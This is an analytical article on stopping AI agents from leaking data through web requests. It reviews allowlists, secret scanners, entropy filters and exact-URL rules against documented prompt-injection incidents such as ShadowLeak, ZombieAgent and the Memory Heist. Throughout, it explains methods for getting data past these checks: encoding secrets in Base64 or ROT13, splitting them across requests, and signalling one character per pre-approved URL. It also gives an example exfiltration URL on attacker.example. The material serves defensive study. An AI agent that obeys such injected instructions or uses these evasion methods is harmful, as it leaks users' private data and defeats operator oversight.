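Forwarding can also happen inside a content delivery network (CDN), which serves many customers' sites from shared machines. In domain fronting, a program puts a permitted host name in the unencrypted opening of the connection and a different one inside the encrypted request. If the CDN routes the request by the inner name, a firewall that reads only the outer name can let through a request to a site that isn't on the allowlist. Docker, whose software runs agents in sandboxes, describes this weakness as inherent to HTTPS proxying. A proxy that decrypts the traffic can compare the two names. The risk is greatest for agents that can run their own programs, since a simple fetch tool takes one URL and doesn't let the model set the two names separately.

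### Why a research agent cannot use a short list

Suppose someone asks an agent why a washing machine shows an error code. The answer may be on the manufacturer's site, in a repair forum or on a blog that neither the user nor the operator has heard of. The agent finds these sites by searching, so nobody can list them all beforehand. If 30% of the pages it needs are on unlisted hosts, the allowlist blocks 30% of its legitimate fetches, even when there are no attacks.

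Anthropic acknowledges this drawback in the network requirements for a Claude app that searches scientific literature. The search services have known addresses, but free copies of articles are on whatever server their authors or publishers chose, so users can expect some downloads to fail on a network that permits only listed hosts. NVIDIA finds a universal list hard to define even for coding agents, because people use the agents for such varied work. It recommends asking the user about cases the list does not cover.

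An agent that enters invoices into one accounting system has no such difficulty, because its operator can list a single host and lose almost nothing. In *Building Browser Agents*, Aram Vardanyan (2025), founder of the software company FillApp, draws on a year of running a commercial browser agent and concludes that prompt injection makes general-purpose autonomous browsing fundamentally unsafe. He favours specialised agents whose limits are written in ordinary code. This is good advice where the task allows it, but such agents can't do the open-ended research that many people want a browsing agent for.

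A short list also doesn't protect against attacks from the listed sites themselves. Once an operator lists the pharmacy from the earlier example, the allowlist lets the injected search for Ben's medicine through.

### What Codex and Claude Code permit by default

Coding agents fall between these extremes. They do much of their work on local files, and an operator can list most of the package registries they need. OpenAI and Anthropic therefore restrict network access for the commands a coding agent runs more tightly than would be practical for a general browsing agent.

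By default, Codex runs commands on a user's own machine with the network off, according to OpenAI's documentation as of June 2026. Turning on network access gives those commands unrestricted access, with no allowlist, unless the user also enables a separate network proxy, which is off by default, or an administrator has imposed network rules.

OpenAI's *Agent internet access* describes the cloud version of Codex, where setup scripts have full internet access but the agent starts offline. Codex removes any setup secrets before the agent starts. An operator who turns on the agent's network access can write an allowlist from scratch, permit all domains, or choose a preset of about 70 domains common in software development. The preset includes `github.com`, `google.com` and `azure.com`, whose owners all host content for outsiders.

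The operator can also limit requests to GET and two other methods that normally only retrieve information. That would stop file uploads like the one used against Cowork, because they need POST. A Google Forms submission sent by GET would still get through if the allowlist entry for `google.com` also covers `docs.google.com`.

Claude Code originally asked the user before every command that needed the network. Anthropic's *Configure the sandboxed Bash tool* describes a sandbox that users can enable instead, where the operating system restricts shell commands and any programs they start. The sandbox denies network access by default. A proxy outside it checks each domain, and Anthropic says a new domain normally triggers a permission request. Claude Code's cloud sessions start out more permissive than Codex's, because their default environment has a level of network access that Anthropic calls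 "Trusted".

These settings mainly govern commands, while the agent's web tools may follow other rules. Codex can search the web even when its commands are offline. By default it reads results only from OpenAI's index and does not contact the live page, so the page's owner receives no request that could carry data. Its full-access mode switches to live results. The Cloud Security Alliance warns that web search and web fetch in Claude Cowork bypass the network egress controls entirely. Shortening Cowork's domain list therefore restricts the code the agent runs but not the pages it fetches. Protection for those fetches has to come from the web tools' own rules, such as a check on the exact URL.

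## Can scanning the URL for secrets tell the two apart?

An operator who cannot list every site a research agent will need can let the agent contact unknown hosts, but scan each outgoing request and block any that contains a secret or text that looks like one. Security teams call this content inspection or data loss prevention (DLP). It works against a password or API key sent in its usual form. It is poor at separating injected fetches from legitimate ones, because a planted instruction can make the agent rewrite the secret before sending it, and many legitimate URLs contain strings that resemble secrets.

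### Getting at the text of a request

A scanner needs the complete URL, which a decrypting proxy or the tool interface can supply. *Connection Escrow* (Gopalakrishna, 2026) demonstrates a third way to read requests. A small program in the Linux kernel copies the data the agent's software passes to its encryption library, just before the library encrypts it. The agent keeps its encrypted connection to the real server, so nobody has to issue a substitute certificate.

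The same work shows why a scanner has to check every request. HTTP clients often reuse one connection for several requests, so checking only the first lets later ones through. In the demonstration, a harmless request and an exfiltrating one shared a connection, and the server received only the harmless one. But Gopalakrishna leaves open how to judge the content and supplies only a placeholder classifier.

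The scanner also has to split the URL into its parts correctly. Mishra (2026), in *Boundary-Mutation Testing for Pattern-Based Secret Detection*, tested scanners that developers use to find credentials in source code. One of them, Gitleaks 8.21.2, recognised nine of the ten credential types tested. For six of those nine, its rules accept a credential only if a quotation mark, a space, the end of the text or one of a few other characters follows it. An ampersand is not one of those characters, so Gitleaks misses these six types in an ordinary query string such as `?key=SECRET&next=1`.

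An operator can avoid this fault by splitting the query into separate values before scanning, so that the scanned text ends where each value ends. TruffleHog, another scanner in Mishra's test, recognised an AWS access key only when the matching secret key appeared in the same file, but a URL may carry just one of the two. Both tools work well on the source code they were designed for, but an operator should test them on URLs before relying on them there.

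### Keywords, known secrets and formats

A keyword filter searches the URL for words that often accompany secrets. The filter in *Silent Egress* blocks URLs that contain `password`, `secret`, `token`, `auth`, `credential`, or one of several spellings of "API key". It matches the label on a value rather than the value itself, so it would block `?password=hunter2` but allow `?q=hunter2`. It would also block a newspaper's `/authors/` page, which contains the letters `auth`, and a help page on resetting a password.

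Exact matching avoids those mistakes by searching for the secrets themselves. The operator gives the scanner a list of the company's API keys, or fingerprints of them, and the scanner blocks any request that contains one of those keys. A long random key almost never appears in a legitimate URL by chance, so false alarms are rare.

Exact matching works well for secrets that are long, random and known in advance. Much of what a browsing agent can leak has none of these properties. Words in a user's mail, such as "metformin", also appear in ordinary searches.

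Operators can also plant fake secrets, known as honeytokens or canaries, where the agent will read them. No legitimate task uses a canary, so its appearance in a request is strong evidence of an attack. Chauhan and Revankar (2026), in *Caught in the Act(ivation)*, give a simple formula for how often this works. If the agent's context holds m real credentials and k canaries, and the attacker takes one at random, the chance of detection is

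k/(m + k) × (1 − β)

where β is the share of leaked canaries that the scanner misses. Three canaries beside one real key would therefore expose at most 75% of such attacks. The formula assumes that neither the attacker nor the agent can tell which key is real. If something in the context shows which key opens the user's database, the attacker can ask for that one. A canary also does nothing for an attacker who wants a paragraph of mail and not a key.

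Scanners rely on format to find secrets that the operator does not know. Many services issue keys with a fixed prefix and length, which a pattern can match. The open-source scanner *detect-secrets* combines patterns for services such as AWS, GitHub and Slack with keyword and entropy checks. Format rules cannot detect most of a user's correspondence, because it has no fixed format.

All these methods look for particular characters, and an agent can change the characters without losing the information. Base64, a standard way of writing binary data as letters, digits and a few symbols, turns a recognisable key into a string that matches neither the key nor its format. A scanner can decode Base64 before searching for secrets, as GitGuardian's commercial scanner does with its *Base64 Generic high entropy secret* rule, but it needs a separate decoder for every other encoding the agent might use.

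### What an entropy threshold measures

An entropy check tries to recognise secrets without knowing their value or format. Random keys use many different characters with little repetition, while ordinary words repeat a few common letters. Claude Shannon's formula from 1948 expresses this difference as a number. For each distinct character c in a value, let p(c) be the share of the value's characters that are c. The entropy in bits per character is

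H = −Σ p(c) log₂ p(c)

where the sum runs over the distinct characters. The string `aaaa` has an entropy of 0, because one character makes up all of it. In `abcd` each character has a share of 1/4, so each contributes (1/4) × 2 bits and the total is 2.

The entropy filter in *Silent Egress* blocks a URL parameter if its value has more than 10 characters and an entropy above 4.0. A value of n characters has the highest possible entropy when all its characters differ. Each character then has a share of 1/n, so the entropy is log₂(n). Since log₂(16) is exactly 4, the filter cannot block any value shorter than 17 characters, and the stated minimum length has no effect.

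The number of symbols also limits entropy. Hexadecimal text uses 16 symbols, the digits and the letters a to f, so its entropy cannot exceed 4.0 at any length. The filter would let through a hexadecimal copy of an entire email. Numbers use only ten symbols and cannot exceed 3.32, so card numbers and phone numbers would pass too.

The results for some sample values show how poorly the score tracks secrecy.

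| Value, after URL decoding | Characters | Entropy (bits per character) | Filter's decision |
|---|---|---|---|
| `metformin` | 9 | 2.95 | allow |
| `ben.ellis@example.com` | 21 | 3.59 | allow |
| `SECRET_API_KEY_12345` | 20 | 3.85 | allow |
| `why does my washing machine show error code e18` | 47 | 3.86 | allow |
| Any lower-case hexadecimal string | any | at most 4.00 | allow |
| `abcdefghijklmnopq` | 17 | 4.09 | block |
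| A random Base64 signature | 44 | about 4.9 on average | block |

*Silent Egress* uses `SECRET_API_KEY_12345` as its example of a key to steal, but the paper's own filter would allow it. A threshold low enough to catch the key would also block the question about the washing machine, which scores slightly higher. The first 17 letters of the alphabet exceed the existing threshold, though they aren't secret. Entropy measures how varied the characters are, and a short sentence from a private email is about as varied as a short search query.

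Signed download links can contain signatures like the one in the last row, and the filter would block these links even when the user wants the file. The filter allows the link if the storage service writes its signatures in hexadecimal, so the result depends on the encoding, not on who asked for the download.

Existing scanners try to reduce these errors by setting separate thresholds for different alphabets. According to the documentation of Classifyre, which builds on *detect secrets*, the defaults are 4.5 for Base64 text and 3.0 for hexadecimal. A random 32-digit hexadecimal key scores about 3.6 on average, so the hexadecimal threshold would catch it, but would also flag the hashes and identifiers that websites put in their own URLs. The Base64 threshold misses secrets shorter than 23 characters, because strings that short can't reach 4.5. *AssetHarvester* (2024), a study of secrets in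 source code, found that entropy checks also rejected low-scoring secrets that protected real databases and other assets.

### How often ordinary web content looks secret

Gorijala (2026), in *SecretSifter*, measured false alarms on code from 56 web applications belonging to one organisation. The code contained 198 values that Gorijala wanted the scanners to find, mostly keys and other credentials. SecretFinder, a scanner with broad patterns, found 63 of them and raised 1,402 false alarms. Its patterns for identifiers, hexadecimal strings and Base64 text also matched the fingerprints that software tools add to file names and code. TruffleHog raised 8 false alarms but found only 71 of the values (35.9%).

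Gorijala's own scanner did better, finding 158 values and raising 24 false alarms. It checks the context of a match, for example by requiring a vendor's name near a string that could be that vendor's key. Gorijala developed it knowing which credentials this organisation used, so it could do worse on other sites. The test scanned content that servers deliver to browsers, not the URLs that agents request. It still shows how common random-looking strings are on the web, and a browsing agent copies many of them from links into its own requests.

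If leaks are rare, a scanner that wrongly flags even a few fetches per hundred will raise far more false alarms than real ones. Suppose one fetch in 10,000 leaks a secret, and a scanner catches every leak but wrongly flags 1% of legitimate fetches. Out of 10,000 fetches, it blocks one leak and about 100 legitimate fetches. An operator can narrow the rules to stop the false alarms, but the scanner then misses more leaks. *A Comparative Study of Software Secrets Reporting by Secret Detection Tools* (2023) found that GitHub's scanner had the fewest false alarms, with three quarters of its reports correct, but that it detected only 6% of the secrets.

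### The filters in Silent Egress

*Silent Egress*, a February 2026 paper by eBay researchers, tested keyword and entropy filters on an agent under attack. The agent ran on `qwen2.5:7b`, a small open model, with sensitive data placed directly in the text it read. The user always asked for a summary of a web page. The researchers hid instructions in the page's title, description, body or link text, and a server they controlled recorded any data that arrived.

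They varied where the injection was placed, whether the agent reached the page directly or through redirects, and whether the instructions asked for the data in one request or in four pieces. They ran each of the 16 combinations 30 times, for a total of 480 runs. The agent sent a request to the attacker's server in 423 of them, or 88%. As mentioned earlier, output checks missed 95% of these attacks.

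To compare eight defences, the researchers used the combination with the injection in the page body, no redirect and no splitting. They ran it 30 times without any defence and 30 times under each defence.

| Defence in *Silent Egress* | Runs in which the agent tried to send data | Runs in which data got out |
|---|---|---|
| None | 100% | 100% |
| Security instructions in the system prompt | 66.7% | 66.7% |
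| Tags marking web content as untrusted | 100% | 100% |
| Both of these prompt defences | 56.7% | 56.7% |
| Domain allowlist | 100% | 0% |
| "Redirect detection" | 83.3% | 0% |
| Keyword filter | 23.3% | 0% |
| Entropy filter | 0% | 0% |
| All defences together | 0% | 0% |

The attempt rates in the table give reason to doubt that both content filters work as perfectly as they appear to. These filters act after the model has written its request, so adding one should not change how often the model tries to send data, unless the model receives information about the filter. Yet attempts fell from 100% to 23.3% under the keyword filter and to zero under the entropy filter, so the entropy filter never had anything to block.

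The paper suggests that the model avoids high-entropy values when it is under such monitoring, but the filter it describes gives the model no way to know about the monitoring. The paper attributes the low figure for the keyword filter to the model encoding or reformatting the secret in some runs. But a reformatted secret would have passed the filter and reached the attacker, and the paper reports no leaks in that condition. An unreported change to the prompt or an error in counting attempts could explain both results. Until someone repeats the test, the two zeros are weak evidence that keyword or entropy filters stop attacks.

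The allowlist result is easier to interpret, because the agent attempted the injected request every time. But the test used an attacker domain that no sensible list would include, so it leaves out attackers who use an approved service. The "redirect detection" blocks numeric addresses, certain domain endings such as `.xyz`, and paths containing words such as `exfil` and `collect`. The paper's own attack examples send the data to a path named `/collect`, which contains one of those blocked words. The check does not follow redirects, and the comparison used none.

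For an egress policy, the paper's most serious omission is that it doesn't measure how many legitimate requests the filters would block. A filter that blocked every request would also have scored zero leaks in this comparison. The paper reports a false-positive rate of zero, but this means only that the agent never contacted the attacker's server in 120 runs with harmless pages, which shows that the injections caused the leaks.

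The researchers acknowledge that they made conditions easy for the attacker and tested only one model. They argue that larger models could be more vulnerable because such models follow instructions better, but they did not test any. Their results show that an agent can leak data while giving a normal answer, but not how often current agents do so.

### Splitting the secret across requests

In half of the 480 runs, the planted instructions told the agent to split the secret into four pieces and send each in its own request, so the attacker could rejoin them afterwards. The researchers call this sharded exfiltration. In their example, the fragments are `SECR`, `ET_A`, `PI_K` and `EY_1`, which would leave out the last four characters of the example key.

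Sharding defeats the filters described above. A four-character fragment has an entropy of at most 2, so an entropy filter with a threshold of 4.0 ignores it. Exact matching fails because no request contains the whole key, and keyword matching misses the fragment `SECR` because it does not contain `secret`. *Silent Egress* states that sharding bypasses simple DLP. This reasoning supports the claim, but the researchers tested their filters only against unsplit secrets.

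The agent contacted the attacker's server in 238 of the 240 runs that asked for one request, but in only 185 of the 240 runs with longer instructions that asked for four. The paper defines a completion rate, the share of runs in which all the pieces arrive, but never reports it. It is therefore unclear in how many of those 185 runs the attacker received only part of the secret.

The paper measures how visible the leak is with Leak@k, the share of runs in which sensitive data appears somewhere in the first k requests. Leak@1 was 0.967 for unsplit secrets and 0.263 for sharded ones, a drop of 73%. The paper also reports a Leak@3 of 0.158 for sharded secrets, which contradicts its own definition. Any run with sensitive data in its first request also has sensitive data in its first three, so Leak@3 must be at least as high as Leak@1.

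The value of 0.263 is also odd. Leak@1 counts a run even if only a fragment of the secret appears, and the first request of a sharded attack should already contain a fragment. Leak@1 should therefore be close to 77%, the share of runs that reached the attacker. Perhaps the measurement recognised only some of the fragments. If so, the drop shows how well sharding hides a leak from a matching program, not that the first request leaked less.

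A scanner with a list of known keys could search URLs for pieces of them, but it would have to block more legitimate requests as the pieces got smaller. A random 20-character key contains 17 overlapping four-character pieces. With a 64-symbol alphabet, there are nearly 17 million possible pieces of that length, so accidental matches would be rare. If the attacker asks for two-character pieces, there are only 4,096 possible pairs, and the key contains 19. A legitimate URL with 100 random-looking characters would then contain at least one of those 19 pairs more than a third of the time.

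The alternative is to add up small leaks over a whole session. Chauhan and Revankar built a monitor that estimates how much each of an agent's replies reveals about a secret and keeps a running total. They tested it on 50 synthetic 20-turn conversations in which an attacker extracted a secret little by little. Searching each reply for the secret caught none of the attacks, while the running total caught 90%.

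The attacks the monitor missed came early in the conversation and ended before the total reached the limit. An attacker could also start a new session to reset the count. The monitor reads only the agent's replies, so it would miss a secret in a URL, which is part of a tool call. The researchers call credentials in tool calls "a severe structural blind spot" of their prototype. A running total could be applied to URLs, but their experiment does not show how well it would work there.

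### Changing the wording and the encoding

*The Framing Gap* (Rahman and Kim, 2026) tested what happens when an attacker adapts to the defence. The agent receives a request to summarise a page, the page's text, a made-up secret (`SECRET_12345`), and a policy that it may send the secret only to one trusted host. It then makes a single decision, either to answer or to call a tool that posts data to a URL. The tool only records the call, so no data leaves the machine. An attack counted as successful if the agent leaked the secret after reading the poisoned page but not after reading a clean one.

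Ten kinds of plainly worded attack produced no leaks in 200 trials against OpenAI's `gpt-4o`. The researchers then presented sending the secret as a routine part of the task. `gpt-4o` leaked the secret in every trial when a page described it as a checksum the request needed, and also when a page described it as a configuration value. Across all eight versions in this group, including a baseline that kept the plain wording, it leaked in 40% of trials. Five of the six models in the study leaked far more often under the new wordings than under the plain ones.

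Success depended heavily on wording. When the researchers paraphrased the checksum page five times, the success rate ranged from 0% to 100% across the versions. An attacker who tries three of these paraphrases would succeed with at least one about 96% of the time. Writing an effective page from scratch was harder, and 13 new pages failed in all 130 trials. The percentages therefore measure how well these particular pages worked, not how often agents leak in general.

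These attacks also make the outgoing request look more ordinary. `gpt-4o` added the secret to its message as a signature, and legitimate requests often carry signatures. A scanner could still detect the secret by searching for its exact string, so the researchers built a guard that blocks any request containing that string unless it goes to the trusted host.

They then asked the agent to alter the secret before sending it. Without a guard, the agent leaked the secret in 56.7% of trials across the unaltered version and five simple alterations, such as reversing it or writing it in Base64. With the exact-match guard, it still leaked in 50%. The guard blocked every leak of the unaltered secret but none of the altered versions.

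A second guard, built to reverse exactly those five alterations before searching, reduced leaks to zero in 120 trials. The researchers then tried three encodings that the guard could not decode. With ROT13, which replaces each letter with the one 13 places further along the alphabet, the secret got past the guard in all 20 trials. The other two encodings produced no leaks, for reasons unrelated to the guard. In a separate check, `gpt-4o` could not write one of them, base32, correctly. It could write the other, which shifts each letter by three places, but did not follow the page's instruction to use it.

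Adding ROT13 to the decoder would stop that version until the attacker picked another encoding. An entropy filter would not help, because ROT13 replaces each letter with a fixed substitute. The same character counts now belong to different letters, so the entropy is unchanged.

Revankar, Chauhan and colleagues (2026) similarly found in *MIRAGE* that a detector reading only an agent's output did barely better than guessing on encoded leaks in 126 scenarios, with an AUROC of 0.518. *An Application-Layer Multi-Modal Covert-Channel Reference Monitor for LLM Agent Egress* (2026) notes that a DLP scanner would pass a message that encodes a key in its spacing.

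Rahman and Kim also tested two defences that do not read the outgoing data. A domain allowlist eliminated leaks under every wording and encoding. Splitting the agent so that the part reading the page never held the secret had the same effect, and 9 of 10 summaries of clean pages were still usable. The researchers note that both results follow largely from the design.

A separate model that checked incoming pages for instructions to disclose or encode a secret flagged all 80 reworded attacks and no clean pages. The researchers treat this result as an upper limit because the model's prompt described the kind of attack to look for. The classifiers in *AI Agents May Always Fall for Prompt Injections* did far worse on attacks without telltale phrases.

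The models in the study are old by late 2026. `gpt-4o` dates from 2024, and the other five are small or of a similar age, so the leak rates are weak evidence about current agents. The finding about the guards depends less on the model, because a scanner that cannot decode ROT13 will miss a secret encoded that way, whichever model writes it. More capable models can probably write more encodings correctly. A larger limitation is that the agent had only one step, so it could not retry after the guard refused a request or split the secret across several requests. The researchers leave both possibilities open.

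They also tried some of the reworded pages on ChatGPT, using their own account and a made-up secret. The secret leaked in none of 48 valid trials, which is compatible with a true rate of up to 7.4%. They could not determine whether the model, its instructions or a filter was responsible. They looked for the secret only in ChatGPT's replies, so the result does not show whether the product would have stopped a leak through a URL.

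### Where inspection is worth having

Scanning URLs for secrets works best when nobody is trying to evade the scan. Suppose an agent is debugging a program and pastes a failing URL, including the user's API key, into a search engine. The key is unencoded, so a scanner that checks for the vendor's key format or for the company's known keys will catch it. An allowlist would not block the request, because the search engine is an approved destination.

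Inspection also stops attackers who don't disguise what they steal. In PromptArmor's demonstration against OpenClaw, the attacker's log showed an API key and a name in plain text. A scanner that checked the agent's message before it reached Telegram could have recognised the key, but nothing would have marked the name as a secret to block.

This favours a short set of precise rules. An operator can block requests that contain a known key, a canary or a string in a vendor's distinctive format, and expect few complaints from users. A general entropy threshold is harder to justify for a browsing agent because it blocks legitimate signed links but allows any secret in hexadecimal. Neither kind of rule would stop Ben's agent from searching the pharmacy for metformin, because the URL contains one common word, spelled normally, in the shop's search field.

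## Does it help to allow only URLs that are already known?

An exact-URL rule permits a request only if the complete address is already known from an approved source. It prevents an agent from writing private data into a URL, which is how most of the attacks described so far worked. The operator does not have to list trustworthy websites or recognise the private data. OpenAI and Anthropic have both built such rules into their products. But an attacker can prepare a set of URLs in advance and have the agent reveal data by choosing among them, so the protection depends on who can get a URL approved.

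### Why the rule blocks a URL built around a secret

A domain allowlist requires an operator to decide which sites to trust. In January 2026, OpenAI announced a different test, which checks whether the exact URL already existed on the public web independently of the user's data.

Suppose a planted instruction tells an agent to add the user's API key to the end of `https://attacker.example/collect?data=`. Almost nobody else has the key, so no public page links to the resulting URL and no web crawler has recorded it. The tool can refuse the request without detecting the key. Encoding the key first does not help the attacker, because the encoded version also produces a URL that nobody has seen.

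The rule also deals with open redirects, which OpenAI gives as one reason lists of trusted sites are not enough. To send data through a redirect on a reputable site, the agent must put the data in the redirect's URL. That URL is then not already known, so the rule does not allow it. The owner of a redirect that is already public can change where it leads, but an agent that follows it still sends only the public URL.

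Restricting fetches to known URLs works only if the tool compares the whole URL and then requests exactly what it compared. If the tool ignores the query during the comparison, an injection could make the agent request any known page on the attacker's site with a secret added after the question mark. Developers may want to ignore the query because many sites put harmless tracking codes there, but a tool that removes it before comparing must also remove it from the request.

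### ChatGPT's first URL check

Johann Rehberger, who writes the blog Embrace The Red, reported the underlying leak to OpenAI in April 2023. ChatGPT would display an image from any address, so an injection could leak part of the conversation through an image URL. He also reported the flaw in Microsoft's Bing Chat. According to Embrace The Red, Microsoft fixed it in May 2023 with a Content Security Policy that generally prevented images from loading, while OpenAI took until December.

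Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability* describes OpenAI's first fix. Before displaying an image, ChatGPT's web page sent the image's URL to an OpenAI service called `url_safe`. If the service flagged the URL as unsafe, the browser did not request the image. The service correctly flagged a test URL with an email address in its query.

OpenAI did not publish the criteria, and Rehberger wondered whether the service looked images up in Bing's index. He then tried 36 image URLs on his own site, one for each letter and digit. Nine passed, including the one for "a", while the one for "d" failed for no reason he could see. He used URLs of this kind to send the word "hi" to his server, one letter per request.

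The check ran in ChatGPT's web page, so each of the other apps needed its own version. The iPhone app did not have one at first, and Rehberger later found that the Mac app didn't either. The security company Tenable found more ways around the check. eSecurity Planet's *ChatGPT Bugs Put Private Data at Risk* describes one that sent data a character at a time through the redirect links Bing uses for tracking. Tenable reported its findings to OpenAI in December 2024 and stated in its advisory that OpenAI had not yet deployed a solution (Tenable, 2025).

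### ShadowLeak

In June 2025 the security company Radware reported a larger gap. The `url_safe` check covered images that the user's browser was about to load, but ChatGPT's Deep Research mode, which browses the web and then writes a report, opened pages from OpenAI's own servers. Radware's *ShadowLeak* found no comparable restriction on the URLs that Deep Research could open.

Radware sent a test user an email with hidden instructions. When the user asked Deep Research to go through the day's mail, the agent took an employee's name and address from another message, wrote them into a URL on Radware's server and opened it. The user didn't have to click anything. The employer's network controls could not have blocked the request, because it never passed through that network.

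ChatGPT's other safeguards gave some protection. The agent refused the plainly worded versions of the attack, and at one stage it searched for the suspicious address online instead of opening it. With some later versions, it opened the address but left out the personal data. The attack became reliable once the email told the agent to encode the data in Base64, supposedly for security. Radware reports a 100% success rate in repeated tests but doesn't say how many it ran.

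According to Radware, the model encoded the name and address first, so the software that carried out the request received only a harmless-looking string. Content inspection can miss such strings. An exact-URL rule would have blocked the request, because the encoded data made a URL that had never existed before. OpenAI fixed the flaw in early August 2025.

### ZombieAgent

When Radware tested it again, ChatGPT opened URLs only exactly as it had received them and would not add parameters, even when explicitly told to. *ZombieAgent* describes how Radware got around this restriction in September 2025. The attacker's email listed ready-made URLs on the attacker's server, one for each letter and digit and one for a space. ChatGPT found the private data and opened the URL for each character in order.

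To leak the name "Ben", for example, the agent would open `/b`, then `/e`, then `/n`. Every request exactly matches a URL in the email, and none contains the name. The attacker reads the name from the order of requests in the server's log.

Requests can arrive out of order, so Radware also prepared URLs that included the character's position, such as `/b0`, `/e1` and `/n2`. Covering every letter and digit in ten positions takes 360 URLs. Rehberger suggests stopping the agent from requesting the same URL twice in one session, either by refusing the request or by reusing the first response. This defence would garble a name with a repeated letter if the attacker had only one URL per letter. Numbering would weaken it, because the second "n" in "Anna" would have its own URL, and the defence would have no effect until the positions ran out.

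OpenAI had also restricted where URLs could come from. ChatGPT would not open an attacker's URLs if they were stored in its memory, a feature that keeps notes between conversations. Radware instead used a shared file to plant a standing instruction in memory, which told ChatGPT to read an email containing the URLs before answering the user. Because ChatGPT still accepted URLs from email, the ban on URLs from memory did not stop the leak, which could now recur in every new conversation.

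Bugcrowd, which handles vulnerability reports for OpenAI, reproduced the attack on September 30, and OpenAI fixed it on December 16. According to the press article *ChatGPT falls to new data-pilfering attack*, after the fix ChatGPT would no longer open a link from an email unless the link appeared in a well-known public index or the user had supplied it in the chat.

### OpenAI's public index

According to OpenAI's January 2026 announcement, a crawler with no access to user data builds the index by recording URLs from public pages, as a search engine does. An agent can load a page or image automatically only if its exact URL is in the index.

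If the URL is not in the index, OpenAI treats it as unverified and either tells the agent to try a different website or warns the user that the link may share information from the conversation. The user can still open the link from the warning, so the warning protects only people who heed it. Rehberger believes that once a user types a URL, ChatGPT also accepts it for the rest of that chat.

Allowing only known URLs is a stronger rule than the one ZombieAgent defeated. Under the earlier rule, the URL only had to reach the agent in finished form, which an attacker could arrange by sending an email. Now the attacker has to publish the URLs and wait for the crawler to find them before the agent will fetch any.

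An attacker who already runs a website may have little or no wait for pages to be indexed. Rehberger notes that a large blog probably has 36 indexed pages already, and an injection could assign a letter or digit to each. The pages can be ordinary articles whose addresses don't suggest a code. He adds that OpenAI's technical paper on the rule acknowledges this bypass. How much an attacker can learn this way depends on the number of prepared pages and the number of requests the agent makes.

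The index can also contain private links. If someone posts a confidential download link on a public forum, the crawler may record it, and the agent can then open it without a warning. OpenAI therefore claims only that a public URL is "much less likely" to contain the user's private data.

A more practical weakness is that the index check can miss some requests. Rehberger dates the new checks to about August 2025, but ZombieAgent still worked in late September with URLs from an email. The December repair suggests that the index check did not cover such links until then. Rehberger expects more gaps like this because developers who add features to ChatGPT may not know that the new requests need the check. The phone app and Deep Research had already had such gaps.

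OpenAI's announcement gives no figures for attacks stopped or for legitimate links that fail the check, so the case for the rule rests mainly on the reasoning about composed URLs. That reasoning is sound for any request that goes through the check, whichever model the agent uses.

### Anthropic's rule for web_fetch

Anthropic had released a different exact-URL rule in September 2025, with a tool called `web_fetch` that lets its Claude models read web pages. The software around the model lets Claude fetch only URLs that have already appeared in approved parts of the conversation. These include the user's messages, search results and, in the original version, pages Claude had fetched earlier.

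Willison (2025), in *Claude API*, tested the rule in the consumer Claude app, using a server that displayed the requests it received. Claude could not open a URL it had constructed itself. Willison considered this ban the most protective part of the design because it stops the most common exfiltration attacks.

He also saw that the approved sources could contain an attacker's text. In the API, which developers use to build their own products on Claude, a "user message" is whatever the developer's program sends in the user's role. A program that summarises mail might paste an entire email into that message, and the tool would treat every link in the email as one the user had supplied. URLs in results from the developer's own tools are approved too, so if one of those tools reads the user's inbox, an attacker can get a list of URLs approved by emailing it to the user, as in ZombieAgent.

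Under Anthropic's rule, then, the URL must exist before Claude decides to fetch it. It can be created during the conversation, and nobody outside the conversation needs to have seen it.

### The Memory Heist

In July 2026 Ayush Paul used this difference to extract personal details from Claude's chat app, in an attack known as the Memory Heist. The app keeps memories of a user's past conversations, so Claude may know the user's name and employer before it opens any page. `web_fetch` could open links on pages it had already fetched, as Willison (2026) explains in *How I tricked Claude into leaking your deepest, darkest secrets*. An attacker's page could therefore supply the next set of permitted URLs.

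Paul's site claimed that AI assistants had to identify their users to get in. It offered a link for each letter of the alphabet and asked Claude to find its user's profile by following them letter by letter. The server generated further links as Claude went. For a user called Ben, Claude might go from `/b` to `/be` to `/ben`. The site showed these pages only to visitors that identified themselves as Claude, which made the attack harder for a person to spot.

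The attack revealed the user's name, home city and employer even though the rule worked as designed. Claude never composed a URL and followed only links that a page had given it, as people do on any website.

In this example, the last URL contains the whole name, even though every URL came from an approved source. The attacker's server could write `/ben` as a link because Claude had already revealed the first two letters by requesting `/be`. So the URL existed before Claude decided to open it, but it still depended on Ben's data. A check against OpenAI's index would reject a link that a server had just made up for one visitor, so the attacker would have to use pages already in the index, as in Rehberger's blog example.

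Anthropic said it had already identified the flaw internally and did not pay Paul a bounty. It fixed the problem by removing the tool's ability to open links from pages it had fetched. Claude could then open only URLs that the user had entered or that its search tool had returned.

### What Anthropic's API permits today

The API still allows link-following by default. Anthropic's *Web fetch 工具*, a Chinese edition of the tool's documentation whose examples use Claude Opus 5.5, lists URLs from earlier fetches among the permitted sources. A developer who gives Claude both private data and this tool, and keeps the default settings, is therefore exposed to the method Paul used.

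Developers can now close the gap themselves with a setting called `url_sources`, which controls separately whether the tool accepts URLs from user messages, from the developer's own tools, and from Anthropic's search and fetch tools. It can also exclude URLs from a single tool. A developer who excludes results from `web_fetch` but keeps those from web search gets roughly the rule the chat app now has.

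The documentation also warns about tools that repeat what Claude has written. If a developer provides a tool that runs Claude's code and returns the output, Claude can write a program that prints a URL containing private data, and the URL then counts as one that came from a tool. An error message that quotes Claude's text has the same effect. By default, `web_fetch` accepts such URLs, so the ban on constructing URLs fails unless the developer excludes the tool. Anthropic excludes its own hosted code-execution tool.

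Anthropic has also added a form of content inspection. The tool refuses a URL that appears to contain a credential, such as an API key or password, unless the credential is in the developer's system prompt or the text of the user's message. This would catch a key that the code-running tool had printed in its usual form, but not Ben's name or a key that the program had encoded first.

An older English edition, Anthropic's *Web fetch tool*, advises developers to use the tool only in trusted environments or with non-sensitive data. If exfiltration is a concern, it suggests turning the tool off, limiting the number of fetches or restricting the domains. A fetch limit restricts how much data an attacker can extract one request at a time, but neither edition sets one by default.

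### Who can get a URL approved

Under OpenAI's rule, an attacker needs a website that the crawler has visited. That takes some preparation but no contact with the victim, and the same pages work against every ChatGPT user whose agent reads the injection. But the attacker can't tailor the URLs to one person during the attack.

With the default settings of Anthropic's API, the attacker only needs to get the agent to read a page or message. The same text can contain both the instruction and the URLs, and the attacker's server can generate new URLs based on the data it has received. Approval lasts for one conversation, but the attacker can get it again in the next one the same way.

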